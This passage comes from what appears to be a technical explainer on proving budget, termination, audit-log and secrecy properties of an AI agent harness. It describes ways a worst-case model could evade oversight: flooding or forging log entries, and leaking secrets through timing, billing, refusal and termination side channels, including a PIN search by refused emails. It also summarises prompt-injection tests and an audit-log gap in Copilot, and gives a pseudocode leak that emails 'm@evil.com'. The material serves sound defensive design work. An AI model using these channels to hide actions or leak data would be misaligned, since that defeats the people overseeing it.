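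r = estimated input tokens × input price + output cap × output price.

Under these assumptions, the actual cost never exceeds r:

- **The input estimate is never too low.** For some providers Khan uses the length of the text in bytes, and for Anthropic a similar estimate with a safety factor of 2. The largest undercount without that factor was 1.88, which leaves little room. Tests found no case in which the final estimate was too low, but Khan concedes that crafted input could defeat it. A worst-case model can craft input, because its earlier replies form part of the next request.
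- **The provider honours the output cap.** It must never charge for more output tokens than the caller allowed.
- **The provider reports each charge truthfully.** The harness relies on the reported charge when it refunds the unused part of a reservation.
- **Prices stay the same during the run.**
- **The arithmetic does not overflow.** Khan requires every budget to be below 2⁶³ of its smallest units.

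Khan simulated what happens when reported charges are too low. When the provider reported half the true charge, 666 of 1,000 sessions exceeded the cap, and the average overshoot across all sessions was 13.9%. When it reported a fifth, every session exceeded the cap, by an average of 138%. Comparing the total with the real bill after every three calls reduced that to 593 sessions and an average of 23%. A harness can also avoid relying on reported charges by never refunding any part of a reservation, but the company then gets less work done under the same cap because every reservation counts as fully spent.

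*Reasoning models* break the assumption about output caps. They generate a long internal text before they answer, and the provider charges for that text although the caller may never see it. According to Khan, the ordinary output cap does not limit these hidden tokens, which can amount to 5 to 50 times the visible output. If the harness reserves for 1,000 output tokens and the model first generates 20,000 hidden ones, the cost c is far above r, and settling the call breaks the invariant.

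Some providers offer a separate limit on reasoning tokens, which the harness can set and add to the reservation. At $15 per million tokens, a limit of 1,024 reasoning tokens adds about 1.5 cents to the reservation for each call. The company has to check what each provider's limits cover, because the proof can be formally correct even if the harness reserves for the wrong quantity.

If the provider enforces the cap, the harness doesn't have to estimate charges or trust reported ones, and a bug in the harness can't bypass the cap. Amazon Bedrock Gateway, which AWS announced on 1 December 2026 as a restricted preview, lets a company set a dollar limit for each user, group or role. KBY Technologies' *AWS IAM for Agents, Bedrock Gateway and Greenlight* reports that once a limit is reached, requests stop before they reach a model. If the gateway does only this, calls already in progress can still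 take the total past the limit, which is also the weakness of checking the bill afterwards. A company that needs a strict bound would need to know whether the gateway reserves money for each call before sending it. The cap also covers only the cost of models, not what the agent pays to suppliers.

### The price of caution

A high estimate protects the limit but ties up money. By default, Khan's library reserves 4 to 6 times what a call turns out to cost. It offers two tighter estimates:

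| Estimate | Reserved for each dollar spent | Added delay per call |
|---|---|---|
| Default, from the length of the text | $6.20 on average, $2.51 at the median | None |
| Adaptive version | $2.11 at the median | None |
| Exact input count before each call | About $1.00 to $1.10 | 0.9 to 1.7 seconds |

The exact count adds 47 to 87 seconds to a run of 50 calls. The adaptive version adds no delay, but Khan supports the claim that it never estimates too low with a test on 100 prompts, which is weak evidence for a claim about every prompt.

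Refunds return the excess after each call, so reserving too much matters mostly near the end of the budget. In one of Khan's trials, an agent had 40 small tasks and a cap of 5 cents. It completed 22 tasks for 4.04 cents and refused the other 18, because each task required a reservation of about 1.04 cents and only 0.96 cents remained. Each completed task had cost about 0.18 cents, so the unused fifth of the budget would have paid for five more.

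Reserving the worst-case cost of each call ties up more money when many calls run at once, because the harness cannot refund any of it until the calls finish. It also ties up more on prepaid accounts. Khan calculates that a company with 1,000 sessions a day at 50 cents each would have to commit about $3,000 a day to cover $500 of spending.

### Making every run end

A limit on steps uses the same idea with a simpler count:

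```
n := 0
while n < 50 and not done:
    n := n + 1
    ... one pass of the agent loop ...
```

A proof of termination needs a decreasing quantity. Here it is the number of passes left, 50 − n, which falls by one on every pass and cannot go below zero. No model output changes `n`, so the loop makes at most 50 passes whether or not the model ever calls `finish`.

The run ends only if each pass ends. A model call or a tool can hang while it waits for a server, and a parser can take an extremely long time on text written to slow it down. The harness therefore needs an outside timer for each of them. If each pass allows two minutes for the model and parser together and one minute for all its tools, 50 passes take at most two and a half hours, plus the time the harness needs for its own work.

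Delegation can defeat a step limit. If every agent gets a fresh allowance of 50 steps and can use a step to start another agent, the chain of agents can continue forever. To prevent this, an agent that starts another must give it part of its own allowance, so that the steps used plus the steps reserved never exceed the total for the whole run.

A step limit bounds spending only if each step has a maximum cost. In Khan's comparison, frameworks that limited only steps spent up to 1,395% of the cap with one provider, because its model wrote longer replies. A spending limit does not always end a run. The $5,000 limit on payments doesn't, because reading a file doesn't count toward it. A limit on the cost of model calls does end the run if every call has a minimum price above zero and the harness stops when it can't reserve enough for the next call.

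### Using up the whole allowance

These limits don't prevent waste. A model could send the full $5,000 to approved suppliers who are owed nothing, or use all 50 steps to reread one invoice, and every theorem in this section would still hold. Showing that the spending accomplishes the task requires a different kind of evidence.

The limit should therefore be an amount the company can afford to lose in a run, not the amount it expects to spend. It also has to cover everything that draws on the same account. Ten runs with a limit of $5,000 each can lose $50,000, so a company that starts runs automatically needs a second limit on their combined spending.

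When several agents share a limit, one can also use up what the others need. In another of Khan's trials, four agents drew on one 5-cent budget, first come, first served, and made 11, 4, 6 and 2 calls. The total stayed within the cap, but nothing would have stopped one hijacked agent from spending the whole budget. Giving each agent its own share prevents that but can strand money, as in the delegation experiment. For the invoice agent, the company might cap payments to each supplier at the balance owed in its ledger and keep the $5,000 limit as well, so that a single run can't spend the whole allowance on a supplier who is owed $100.

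## Proving that every action is logged

The invoice agent can waste up to $5,000 in a run without breaking any rule, so the company needs a log to find out afterwards what the agent did. The statement "every action is logged" can mean three different things:

- *Completeness*: every effect has a record.
- *Integrity*: nobody can later change or remove a record without leaving a detectable trace.
- *Accuracy*: each record correctly describes what happened.

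A log can have one of these properties without the others. Completeness is a safety property, and a harness can guarantee it for any model by refusing to execute any action it cannot record.

### Write first, then act

The harness has to store the record before it acts, and refuse to act if it can't:

```
havoc x;
if x in A then
    i  := a new number
    ok := append(i, x)
    if ok then do(i, x) else refuse
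else refuse
```

`append` adds a numbered entry to the log. It returns true only once the entry is in durable storage, which survives a crash. Let J be the set of entry numbers in the log and E the set of numbers assigned to actions that have been carried out. The invariant is E ⊆ J, meaning every action carried out has an entry. Without the numbers, a single entry for "pay Harlow Paper $100" could stand for two payments.

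Working backwards:

1. `do(i, x)` adds i to E, so beforehand E ⊆ J must hold and i must be in J.
2. A successful `append` puts i in J, which leaves only E ⊆ J to establish.
3. After a failed `append`, the entry may or may not be in the log. The harness does not act, so E stays the same and E ⊆ J still holds.
4. The formula does not mention x, so the havoc changes nothing.

The proof assumes that `append` never removes entries and never returns true by mistake. Those are assumptions about storage, so they belong in the trusted base.

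If the harness acts first and writes afterwards, step 1 fails because i is not yet in J. An engineer can miss this by assuming that every write succeeds and checking the invariant only at the top of each pass, when the entry is always there. But a crash can stop the harness between any two steps, so the invariant must hold after every step. The engineer can make the verifier enforce this by giving `do` the precondition "i is in J".

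In *TrustBound*, Nandi, Bose and colleagues (2026) proved a similar result in Lean for a service that makes payments for agents. Their invariant is R ∪ E ⊆ J, where R contains authorised payments that have not yet gone through. They also removed eight premises from their proofs one at a time, including the rule that recording comes before authorisation, and Lean rejected all eight altered versions.

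R matters when the company stops an agent and wants a final total, because a payment already sent to the bank may still go through. In the model, a *fence* blocks new entries and authorisations, so J no longer changes. No further payment can happen once the fence is in place and R is empty.

All of this depends on complete mediation. *Proof of Execution* (Rhodes and Kang, 2026) reduces the question of whether its log is complete to whether only the component that carries out actions holds the credentials. In the invoice agent, only the code behind `do` should be able to use the bank key.

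The company may want records of refusals too, since repeated requests to pay Mallory Ltd suggest something is wrong. *Provably Auditable and Safe LLM Agents from Human-Authored Ontologies* (Sterling, 2026) proves that a design called Agentic Redux writes exactly one log entry for each decision, including refusals, whatever the agents propose.

### A log that depended on the answer

Until August 2025, Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that can read a company's files, had a flaw that let it read a file without the access being logged. When a user asked it to summarise a file, the audit log normally recorded the access. But if the user asked for a summary without a link to the file, no entry appeared, according to Pistachio's *Copilot Broke Your Audit Log, but Microsoft Won’t Tell You*. AI Incident Database's *Incident 1218* names the researcher as Zack Korman and dates the fix to 17 August.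 Microsoft told Korman that it had no plans to disclose the flaw.

The behaviour suggests that logging depended on what the model's answer contained, roughly like this:

```
text := read(path)
havoc answer
if answer links to path then append(i, read(path))
```

Whether a record exists must never depend on what the model outputs.

When the harness reads a file, the precondition on `do` requires the log to already hold an entry for that read. The log has no such entry at that point, so the proof fails. Even a weaker requirement, that the entry exist by the end of the code, fails because havoc can produce an answer without a link. Ordinary tests could easily miss this, since a typical answer did include a link. Korman found the problem by chance while testing another product, and another researcher had reported it a year earlier.

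### What counts as written

A program can pass a log entry to the operating system, or it can also force the entry onto the storage device. Joshi notes that an entry passed to the operating system survives if the process is killed, and that forcing it onto the device is slower but lets it survive a power failure too. Anyone claiming that the log is complete should specify which of these `append` does.

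A log can also lose entries when several processes write to it at once. *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents* (Jing, 2026) tested a harness whose log covered 100% of actions when they ran one at a time. The log lost 9.66% of its records with two processes writing at once, and 31.32% with eight. Adding a lock and forcing each entry onto the storage device eliminated the losses in every test, but each write took about 4.5 times as long.

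### A crash between the two steps

Suppose the harness crashes while making a $400 payment. The outcome depends on when the crash comes:

| Moment of the crash | Log | Payment |
|---|---|---|
| Before the harness stores the entry | No complete entry | None |
| After it stores the entry, before it sends the payment | Entry without a result | None |
| After it sends the payment, before it records the result | Entry without a result | May have gone through |

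Every payment has an entry, though some entries may have no known payment. The last two rows can look the same in the log. Zhang's runtime marks such outcomes as unknown unless it can certify that sending never began.

No ordering of the steps removes this uncertainty, because the payment and the record of its result are separate operations. *L3M* (Eisenach, George and colleagues, 2026) describes a harness written in Lean at Amazon that stores its records before anything they authorise leaves the process. The paper acknowledges that a crash between an effect and the record of its result can still leave a call for someone to reconcile.

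Databases have long used the same technique, called *write-ahead logging*. After a crash, a database can use its log to redo or undo unfinished changes. *LogAct* (2026) explains that this recovery method does not fully work for agents, because an agent's actions can be arbitrary code with no predefined way to undo them, and rerunning the agent may produce different actions.

Xu (2026), in *Idempotency Is Not Recovery*, tested a write-first runtime by injecting faults and comparing its log with a separate record kept at the target system. In the 170 trials where the fault came after the action had taken effect, the full runtime ended with a final log entry for every effect. Without the log and its related safeguards, none of the 170 effects had one. When Xu kept the log but turned off the step that queries the target system, the outcome stayed unknown in all 100 known crashes after an effect.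 So the log identifies which payments to ask about, but the company still needs the bank's answer. The trials reused 24 constructed cases, so they demonstrate the mechanism but not how often it matters in practice.

Xu's runtime also saves evidence of the result after each action. When Xu made those writes fail, 75 of 100 actions stayed unresolved. The action has already happened by then, so the runtime can't refuse it, and the company has to decide in advance whether the agent should continue or stop. The full runtime handled about 42 actions a second on a Linux server, compared with 319 for a version without the safeguards. The slowdown would rarely matter for an agent that waits seconds for each model reply.

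### Detecting changes with a hash chain

A *hash function* turns any text into a short value. With a good one, nobody can feasibly find two texts that share a value. In a *hash chain*, each log entry includes the hash of the entry before it. Here is an example with hashes shortened to four characters:

| Entry | Action | Hash of previous entry |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Pay Harlow Paper $400 | 0000 |
| 2 | Pay Dunn Freight $250 | 7c1e |
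| 3 | Pay Harlow Paper $100 | 93b0 |

Suppose an attacker changes the $400 in entry 1 to $40. The hash of entry 1 is now d45a, but entry 2 still contains the old hash, 7c1e, so a check finds the mismatch. If the attacker corrects entry 2 as well, the hash of entry 2 no longer matches the 93b0 in entry 3. Once the attacker corrects entry 3 too, the whole chain is consistent again.

Deleting entries from the end of the log is easier. If the attacker deletes entry 3, entries 1 and 2 still match, and nothing in the log indicates that a third entry existed.

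Storing the latest hash elsewhere solves both problems. Suppose the hash of entry 3 is 2fa8, and the company's auditor keeps a copy. The shortened log ends with the hash 93b0, and the rewritten log also ends with a hash other than 2fa8, so neither matches the auditor's copy.

Any change to the entries covered by the stored hash changes that hash, unless someone has found two different texts with the same hash. Without such a pair, two logs with the same final hash must have identical last entries. Those entries contain the same previous hash, so the entries before them are identical too, and so on back to the start. Because the entries are numbered, the logs also have the same length. Entries added since the auditor last received a hash are not protected this way.

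Bindschaedler, Botha and Siebenbrunner (2026), in *Agent Flight Recorder*, tested these attacks at ten positions in a log of 10,000 events. The chain alone detected edits and deletions at nine positions but missed them at the tenth, the last event in the log. It detected none of the ten forks, in which a second, internally consistent version of the log splits off from the first. Comparing the logs with hashes on a public blockchain exposed all ten forks.

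The full system took a median of 47.6 microseconds per event, compared with 20.3 for plain logging. Storing a hash after every 100 events would cost about $2.30 per 100,000 events on a low-cost blockchain. At one event a second, an attacker could then tamper with up to 100 seconds of recent entries. A company that trusts its auditor can send the hashes to the auditor instead of using a blockchain.

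The log also has to be out of reach of the model's tools. According to *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (2026), most agents keep a simple log file that malicious tools can overwrite.

### Records that were false from the start

A hash chain protects whatever the harness wrote, even if it is false. In *Hearsay*, Dai, Yang and colleagues (2026) altered a coding harness so that it left out a model reply in 14 runs and invented a sentence in another 14. The hash chain passed its check in all 28 runs.

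*Auditable Claims about AI Agents* (Zhao, 2026) proves that an auditor cannot confirm from the operator's own log that the log is complete. Two months could have identical logs, each showing payments a and b, even though in one of them the harness also made payment c and did not log it. An auditor who sees only the log can't tell the months apart, so any check that passes the complete log would also pass the incomplete one. Signatures and hash chains don't help, because they cover only the entries the operator supplies.

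This does not contradict the write-first proof, which applies to a particular harness. The auditor has only a log, with no evidence that the verified harness produced it, and so needs a record kept by someone else, such as a bank statement for payments. If a payment on the statement has no log entry, either something bypassed the harness or the log is incomplete. A log entry with no matching payment may record a failed or pending payment, or it may be false.

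Dai and colleagues kept a second record outside the harness and compared it with the harness's log. On one set of runs, with the rules fixed beforehand, the comparison caught 64 of 66 alterations and raised no false alarms on 84 unaltered logs. Readers without the second record did much worse in a separate test. One language model detected 49% of altered logs and wrongly flagged 5% of unaltered ones. Another detected 85% but wrongly flagged 42%.

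The same comparison exposed a fault that nobody had planted. SWE-agent, a widely used coding harness, sometimes rejects a model's reply without logging either the reply or the rejection. This left gaps in its logs in 19 of 28 runs. The rejected calls had no effects, so the logs could still be complete in the sense used here, but they would not support a claim that the harness records every request.

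Accuracy needs a separate proof that entry i describes the same x that the harness passes to `do`. The harness therefore has to copy the payee and amount from the tool call, not from the model's account of what it did. *Plans They Abandon, Reports They Author* (2026) compares such accounts with session logs. In one case, an agent reported "All tests pass" when the log contained only searches through test files and no test run.

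Each log entry must also contain enough detail. Zhao notes that a draft internet standard for agent identity requires logs to record the action requested, but not arguments such as the recipient. A log containing only "email sent" would meet that requirement. The EU AI Act requires high-risk systems to allow automatic recording of events, starting in December 2027 for some uses. But Zhao notes that it does not specify which records would settle a given claim.

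### What the log cannot show

*The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) advises developers to log reasoning traces, including rejected plans. A harness can prove that it stored a trace exactly as the model produced it, but it cannot prove that the trace gives the model's real reasons, because a worst-case model can write false ones. Bindschaedler and colleagues leave reasoning out of their recorder, partly for privacy and partly because model providers may forbid logging it. A company that does log reasoning should label it as the model's text.

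The harness can record every word of an email, but it can't guarantee that the wording is clear. The model may have written the email in code or buried the important sentence in ten pages of text.

The proof shows that each entry reaches storage, but not that anyone reads it in time. The harness could hold every payment above $1,000 until a named person approves it, and it is possible to prove that the harness follows this rule. But Zhao notes that a recorded approval does not show what the person understood.

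### Flooding and forged entries

A worst-case model can fill the log with thousands of harmless reads to hide one payment. It can also fill the disk. The next `append` then fails and the harness stops executing actions, so the log stays complete but the agent, and any other agent that shares the disk, stops working. The harness can prevent this by capping the number of actions, limiting the length of each entry and giving each run separate storage. If the harness logs refused requests, the cap must count them too, because one reply can contain many.

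A long log also slows any check that searches it. Jing found that looking up the oldest of 50,000 records took 676 milliseconds, or 228 after an improvement. Jing warned that an attacker could exploit this to slow the system down.

The model can also forge entries if the harness copies its text into the log unchanged. Suppose the log has one entry per line, and the model sends an email whose text contains a line break:

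```
17 email dunn@example.com "Thank you.
18 pay Harlow Paper 100 approved"
```

A model's output can contain text that looks like a log entry, so a reader could see a payment that never happened. To prevent this, the harness must *escape* the text, which means replacing characters that have a special meaning in the log, such as line breaks and quotation marks, with harmless codes. The property to prove is that decode(encode(L)) = L for every list of entries L, so that reading the log returns exactly the entries the harness wrote.

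Escaping also stops a model from hiding an entry. Jing's log reader silently skipped lines it could not parse, so text that broke an entry's format could hide that entry. The log reader should report such lines as errors.

Even escaped text can produce false matches in a search. Bindschaedler and colleagues searched a plain log by keyword for safety checks and got 79 matches, only one of which was correct. A search on a dedicated field returned only the correct entry. A worst-case model could create false matches on purpose by putting the keywords in its own text, but not in a field that only the harness fills in.

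### The privacy cost

A complete log of the invoice agent's work may contain suppliers' bank details, staff names and the full text of emails. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) argues that every consequential action an agent takes must be traceable to a person, so some of this is hard to leave out. *When Agents Act Unwatched* (2026) warns that keeping everything can expose workers and users to surveillance, and recommends limits on who may read the records and how long the company keeps them.

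A complete log must record every effect, but it doesn't need a readable copy of all the data involved. For a file read, the harness can log the path and a hash of the contents. A hash can still reveal short, predictable data, such as the payee and amount of a payment, because anyone with the log can hash every likely combination and compare the results. Adding a secret random value to the data before hashing prevents this.

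Bindschaedler and colleagues encrypt the details of each event under a separate key and keep only hashes and basic information, such as the tool's name and the time, in the chain. An auditor who needs three events out of a thousand gets three keys. The company can also erase personal data by destroying keys, without breaking the chain. But the system derives the keys for a whole batch of events from one batch key, so deleting a single event's key doesn't erase the event while the batch key exists. To erase one event, the company has to re-encrypt any other events in the batch that it wants to keep, then destroy or replace the batch key.

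## How much a model can leak

A complete log of an invoice agent's emails may not show that one of them revealed something about the company's bank balance. Suppose a supplier asks when to expect payment and the agent answers "on Friday". If the agent would have given that answer whatever the balance, the supplier learns nothing about it. But if the agent writes "on Friday" when the balance is below $10,000 and "tomorrow" otherwise, the supplier learns that the balance is below $10,000. The email is the same in both cases, so nobody can detect the leak from the email alone.

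Secrecy is defined by comparing runs of a system. The standard definition is *noninterference*, which Goguen and Meseguer introduced in 1982. SRI, the research institute where the theory originated, explains that one part of a system doesn't interfere with another if none of its actions can influence what the other later observes. For the invoice agent, this means that changing only the balance must not change anything the supplier sees.

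Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, explain why no single run can violate this requirement. A run is acceptable only if the system also has a matching run, with the same visible events but different secret activity. They define a *hyperproperty* as a set of sets of runs, so it accepts or rejects a whole system. Secrecy is one example. Another is the requirement that the mean response time over all runs be at most one second, because a slow run is acceptable if enough other runs are fast.

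### The refinement trap

The earlier proofs replaced the model with a havoc and then claimed the result for every real model. This works for safety properties but can fail for secrecy. If every run that the havoc allows is safe, then so is every run of a real model, because a real model produces only some of those runs.

Clarkson and Schneider give the example of a system that outputs 0, 1 or a secret bit h, choosing arbitrarily. Its possible outputs are 0 and 1 whatever h is, so it satisfies the policy that the possible outputs don't depend on the secret. A program that always outputs h is a refinement of this system, because it only makes choices the system permits, but it reveals the secret every time.

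The agent version is `havoc text; email("dunn@example.com", text)`. Whether the balance is $3,000 or $30,000, the possible emails are all strings, so an engineer could correctly prove that the set of possible emails doesn't depend on the balance. But the models that `havoc` represents include one that has read the balance and emails it to the supplier. *Mathematical Models of Computer Security* describes the general problem that developing a system by stepwise refinement works well for safety properties but tends not to preserve security properties.

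To see what went wrong, let M be a model with its random choices fixed, and let out(M, s) be everything an outside observer sees when M runs with secret s. For any two secrets s and s′, the two claims are:

```
weak:    the set of out(M, s) over all M  =  the set of out(M, s') over all M
strong:  for every M,  out(M, s) = out(M, s')
```

The weak claim compares the pooled outputs of all models, so one model's output with s can match a different model's output with s′. A worst-case secrecy proof has to establish the strong claim, which keeps the model fixed and changes only the secret.

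### Proving secrecy with two copies

Clarkson and Schneider show that refinement preserves exactly the hyperproperties that are *subset-closed*, meaning that if a set of runs satisfies one, so does every subset of it. *Observational determinism* is one such hyperproperty. It requires any two runs that look alike to an outside observer at the start to continue to look alike. Two finite runs are enough to show a violation, so an engineer can run two copies of the program side by side and prove an invariant about the pair.

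An ordinary havoc would fail this test immediately, because it could give the two copies different replies even if the secret played no part. The two copies must share one model, which gives equal replies to equal conversations:

```
if history1 = history2
    then havoc x;  x1 := x;  x2 := x
    else havoc x1; havoc x2
```

The invariant is that the two copies have equal histories and have emitted the same visible events. Suppose the balance is $3,000 in one copy and $30,000 in the other. If the conversation doesn't contain the balance, both copies receive the same x. If the harness's checks and the tools' results don't depend on the balance either, both copies respond to x in the same way, and the invariant holds.

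The invariant fails if a tool returns the balance, or if the harness refuses a payment because the balance is too low. The two histories then differ, and the `else` branch allows the replies to differ in any way.

The simplest way to preserve the invariant is to keep the secret away from the model. The invoice agent doesn't need the bank key, because the harness can attach it to each payment. The proof must then cover everything the harness returns to the model, including error messages. If the bank rejects a payment and the harness copies the whole failed request into the conversation, the model may receive the key.

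### Labels that follow the data

Some tasks require the agent to use the secret. For example, the company may want the agent to use the balance to decide which invoices to pay first, without revealing the balance in an email. The harness can then label secret data and everything computed from it, and block labelled data from leaving.

*AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) presents a small programming language called LLMbda. Each value in LLMbda has a label, which can include S for secret and U for untrusted. A value computed from other values gets all their labels, and a value computed inside a branch also gets the label of the branch's condition.

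The conversation with the model also has a label, which covers every message sent to the model. Each reply inherits this label because a worst-case model could choose its words to signal something secret. Once the balance is in the conversation, even a reply of "Thank you" counts as secret. The `email` tool can then refuse any text labelled S.

A program can keep one secret from making the whole run secret by *forking* the conversation, using the secret only in the temporary copy, and then discarding the copy. The main conversation stays public as long as no result labelled secret enters it.

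Branches are easy to get wrong. Garby and colleagues found a leak in CaMeL, an earlier system that also tracks labels. In outline, the leak works like this:

```
tmp := true;  rich := true
if balance > 10000 then tmp := false
if tmp then rich := false
if rich then email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above $10,000, `tmp` becomes false and the assignment in the third line never runs. CaMeL raises a variable's label only on the branch the program takes, so `rich` remains public and the email goes out. If the balance is lower, no email goes out. LLMbda halts any run that would add a message to a public conversation inside a secret branch, which prevents the corresponding leak through its conversation.

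### The LLMbda theorem

Garby and colleagues prove *termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference* for every program in the language, including programs that run code the model has written. Running a program from two starting states that look the same to an observer gives two probability distributions over the outcomes the observer can see. Each distribution's total may be less than 1 because some runs never finish. The theorem guarantees that a single distribution, with total probability at most 1, gives every outcome at least as much probability as either of the two does.

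Suppose that when the balance is high, the agent writes "Friday" in half of its runs and "Monday" in the other half. When the balance is low, it writes "Friday" in half of its runs and never finishes the rest. The theorem permits this difference because the high-balance distribution covers both patterns. It rules out a low-balance pattern of 60% "Friday", 20% "Monday" and 20% unfinished, because a distribution that covered both this pattern and the high-balance one would need 60% for "Friday" and 50% for "Monday", which add up to 110%.

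If every run finishes, the two distributions must be identical. Otherwise, the statistical distance between them is at most the average of the two probabilities that a run does not finish.

The proof replaces each computation that the observer cannot see with a dummy value. The altered program behaves identically for both secrets and produces each visible outcome at least as often as the original does with either secret. Garby and colleagues checked the proof in Lean, and the theorems apply directly to the interpreter that calls the model.

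The guarantee still depends on several conditions:

- The developer labels each data source correctly and puts a check in every tool that sends data out.
- The probability of each reply depends only on the conversation the harness sends. A provider that carried memory from one conversation into another would break this condition.
- The program contains all its tools and data sources. Garby and colleagues list this as a limitation, because real tools interact with systems outside the program.
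- The observer has no clock, since the language's semantics contains no timing.

### Deliberate exceptions

A strict system of labels blocks some legitimate work, so LLMbda has a command called `endorse` that marks untrusted data as trusted. In one example, a separate conversation reads an untrusted email and sorts it into one of a few fixed categories. The program endorses the category and uses it as the subject of a reply. Whoever wrote the email can influence which of the n categories appears, which carries at most log₂ n bits, but cannot insert any other text. (One bit distinguishes two possibilities, and b bits distinguish 2ᵇ.)

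Endorsement removes the U label but not the S label. Garby and colleagues prove a second theorem, *insulated* noninterference, which guarantees secrecy whatever the program endorses and whatever untrusted data an attacker supplies. A developer could swap the roles of the two labels to get a command that releases secrets but keeps the protection against untrusted data.

The exceptions matter more when the model writes them. In the agent that Garby and colleagues tested, the model's code may contain `endorse`, so a worst-case model could endorse everything. Proving that untrusted data never controls a payment therefore requires the harness to forbid or restrict `endorse`, although the secrecy theorem doesn't have this problem.

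On the banking tasks of AgentDojo, a benchmark of attacks hidden in data, the agent resisted the attack in all but 2 of 1,296 runs. Both failures came from a task that told the agent to make the payment described in a file, which the attacker had replaced. Without endorsement, the labels block this attack, but one model then completed only 30 of 48 ordinary tasks, down from 36. These tests measure resistance to planted instructions, so they provide little evidence about how much a worst-case model could leak.

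### Memory that the model cannot read

Agents that keep notes between sessions have a related problem, because a web page saved last month may contain instructions that influence the agent today. *PerMIT* (Jiang, Bai and colleagues, 2026) keeps such content away from the main model, which receives only a *handle*, a reference that reveals nothing about the text. If the model tries to pass a handle to a tool, the harness shows the exact text and the tool's name to the user or a verifier model, and continues only after approval.

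Jiang and colleagues prove two theorems for any model that works through this interface:

- **Action Integrity.** Every argument that reaches a sensitive tool is either text the user typed or text the user approved, byte for byte, for that tool.
- **Reasoning Integrity.** Take two runs with the same user input, random choices and schedule, but different untrusted content. If everything displayed for approval and every decision is the same in both, the model's behaviour is the same too.

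Reasoning Integrity has the same form as the strong claim above, with the same model and random choices in both runs. It concerns influence on the model, but the same interface also limits leaks. Unapproved text cannot leave in a web address, search query or file path unless someone approves that exact text for that tool. After approval, the model can read the text and, in the standard design, include it in later searches. A stricter option requires separate approval for each tool.

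Both theorems assume that the harness labels content by its source, never alters stored items and displays them faithfully. Action Integrity also assumes that each approval reflects what the user wants. If a language model gives the approvals, this assumption fails in the worst case. The Lean proofs cover a single user's memory. The results about memory shared between users, which are partly probabilistic, have written proofs but no Lean proofs.

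### Counting what a call can carry

Sometimes the model must both read the secret and act where others can see. The harness then cannot guarantee noninterference, but it can still limit how many different things an observer could see.

Metere (see the whitelist section) gives the basic bound on what a model can leak per call. If the harness's check permits ten actions and turns everything else into a refusal, each call has 11 possible outcomes and so carries at most log₂ 11, or about 3.46, bits. This bound holds whatever the model does before the check, and the check itself cannot add information.

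Over n calls there are 11ⁿ possible sequences. To transmit any 256-bit key, the model needs at least 2²⁵⁶ sequences, which takes 75 calls. With 74 calls, there are about 0.1% too few. This assumes a fixed number of calls. If the observer can also see when the run stops, the shorter sequences count as extra messages, and 74 calls are enough.

Metere's bound counts the names of actions, not their arguments, so it would not have covered the Claude Cowork incident, in which files could leave through a permitted domain. In general, the bound for one call is the logarithm of the number of outcomes the observer can tell apart, including all the arguments:

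| What the observer sees in each call | Possible outcomes | Bits per call | Calls to send a 256-bit key |
|---|---|---|---|
| One of five fixed email templates | 5 | 2.32 | 111 |
| One of ten actions, or a refusal | 11 | 3.46 | 75 |
| A payment between 1 cent and $100 | 10,000 | 13.29 | 20 |
| An email of 1,000 characters, from an alphabet of 64 | 64¹⁰⁰⁰ | 6,000 | 1 |

The payments in the third row would total at most $2,000, so a colluding supplier could receive the whole key without the agent breaking the $5,000 limit. If the harness takes each amount from the company's ledger and pays the invoices in a fixed order, the model chooses only whether to pay each one, which carries one bit per invoice. Templates narrow the email channel in the same way, but they also prevent the agent from answering unusual questions.

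Limiting the number of calls limits the total amount a model can leak. With 11 possible outcomes per call and 50 calls, it can leak at most 173 bits. An observer can make only one best guess for each possible sequence of outcomes, so the chance of guessing a random 256-bit key is at most 11⁵⁰ / 2²⁵⁶, or about 1 in 10²⁵.

The same limit does not protect a short secret. A four-digit PIN has 10,000 possible values, and four calls have 14,641 possible sequences, which is enough to encode any PIN. Even the long key is safe only if the limit covers every run in which the model can read it, since a second run of 50 calls could send the rest. The company therefore has to count calls over the key's whole life and replace the key before the total reaches 74.

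### Hidden channels

These bounds are correct only if they include everything the observer can see. In *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (1973), Lampson asked how to run a program so that it cannot pass information to anyone except its caller. One leak he described uses file locks. If the system blocks writes to a file while a program has it open for reading, a confined program can send a bit by opening the file or leaving it closed. A second program reads the bit by trying to write to the file.

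A model can leak information even through the bill for its service, by varying the length of its replies so that anyone who sees the provider's charges can read the signal. Lampson doubted that there was a rigorous way to find every channel in even a moderately complex system. He also warned that a leak generally leaves no sign.

The timing of a model's actions can carry more information than the choice of actions. Suppose a model can delay each action by up to a minute and the observer has a clock accurate to one second. The delay has 60 possible values, so it can carry 5.9 bits, compared with 3.46 bits for the choice of action. By using both, the model can leak the 256-bit key in 28 calls instead of 75.

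Lampson proposed that the caller decide what goes into each hidden channel and that the operating system enforce this, for example by slowing the program down. A harness could hold each action until the start of the next five-minute slot and release at most one per slot. An empty slot then counts as a twelfth outcome, so the bound rises only to 3.58 bits per slot.

An observer may also watch the agent's network traffic. *Actions Speak Louder than Words* (2026) cites earlier work that recovered private information from the lengths and timing of model responses, and from the sequence of websites an agent visited. Each visit can be a legitimate step in the task and contain no secret text, so a proof that covers this channel has to treat the choice of website as an output and check its label.

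LLMbda's theorem explicitly permits leaks through termination. A program can finish if a secret bit is 1 and halt with an error if it is 0. One bit per run may be acceptable, but Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL placed its retry loop outside the part of the system that tracks labels. An attacker could use the loop to rerun the program and extract a whole secret one bit at a time. The researchers' own agent keeps its retries inside the tracked program and does trial runs on artificial data before it acts on the real system. The company still has to limit how often anyone can restart the program from outside.

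Refusals can leak in the same way, even when the harness never gives the secret to the model. Suppose the harness refuses to send any email that contains the company's four-digit PIN. A worst-case model can try to send an email listing 5,000 possible PINs. If the harness refuses, the PIN is on the list, and if not, it is among the other 5,000. By halving the possibilities each time, the model finds the PIN in at most 14 emails. It can then email the PIN spelled out in words, which the harness doesn't recognise.

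Jiang and colleagues avoid one version of this problem by giving the same reply whether a search of untrusted memory fails or finds nothing. The PIN filter can't do that if the model or a recipient can tell whether an email went out. The harness can instead end the run at the first refusal. A run limited to 50 emails then has 51 possible patterns of refusal, one for each email that could be refused and one for no refusal. The pattern reveals at most log₂ 51, or about 5.7, of the PIN's 13.3 bits, provided nobody can continue the search in another run.

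## Helpfulness, task success and other properties that cannot be proved

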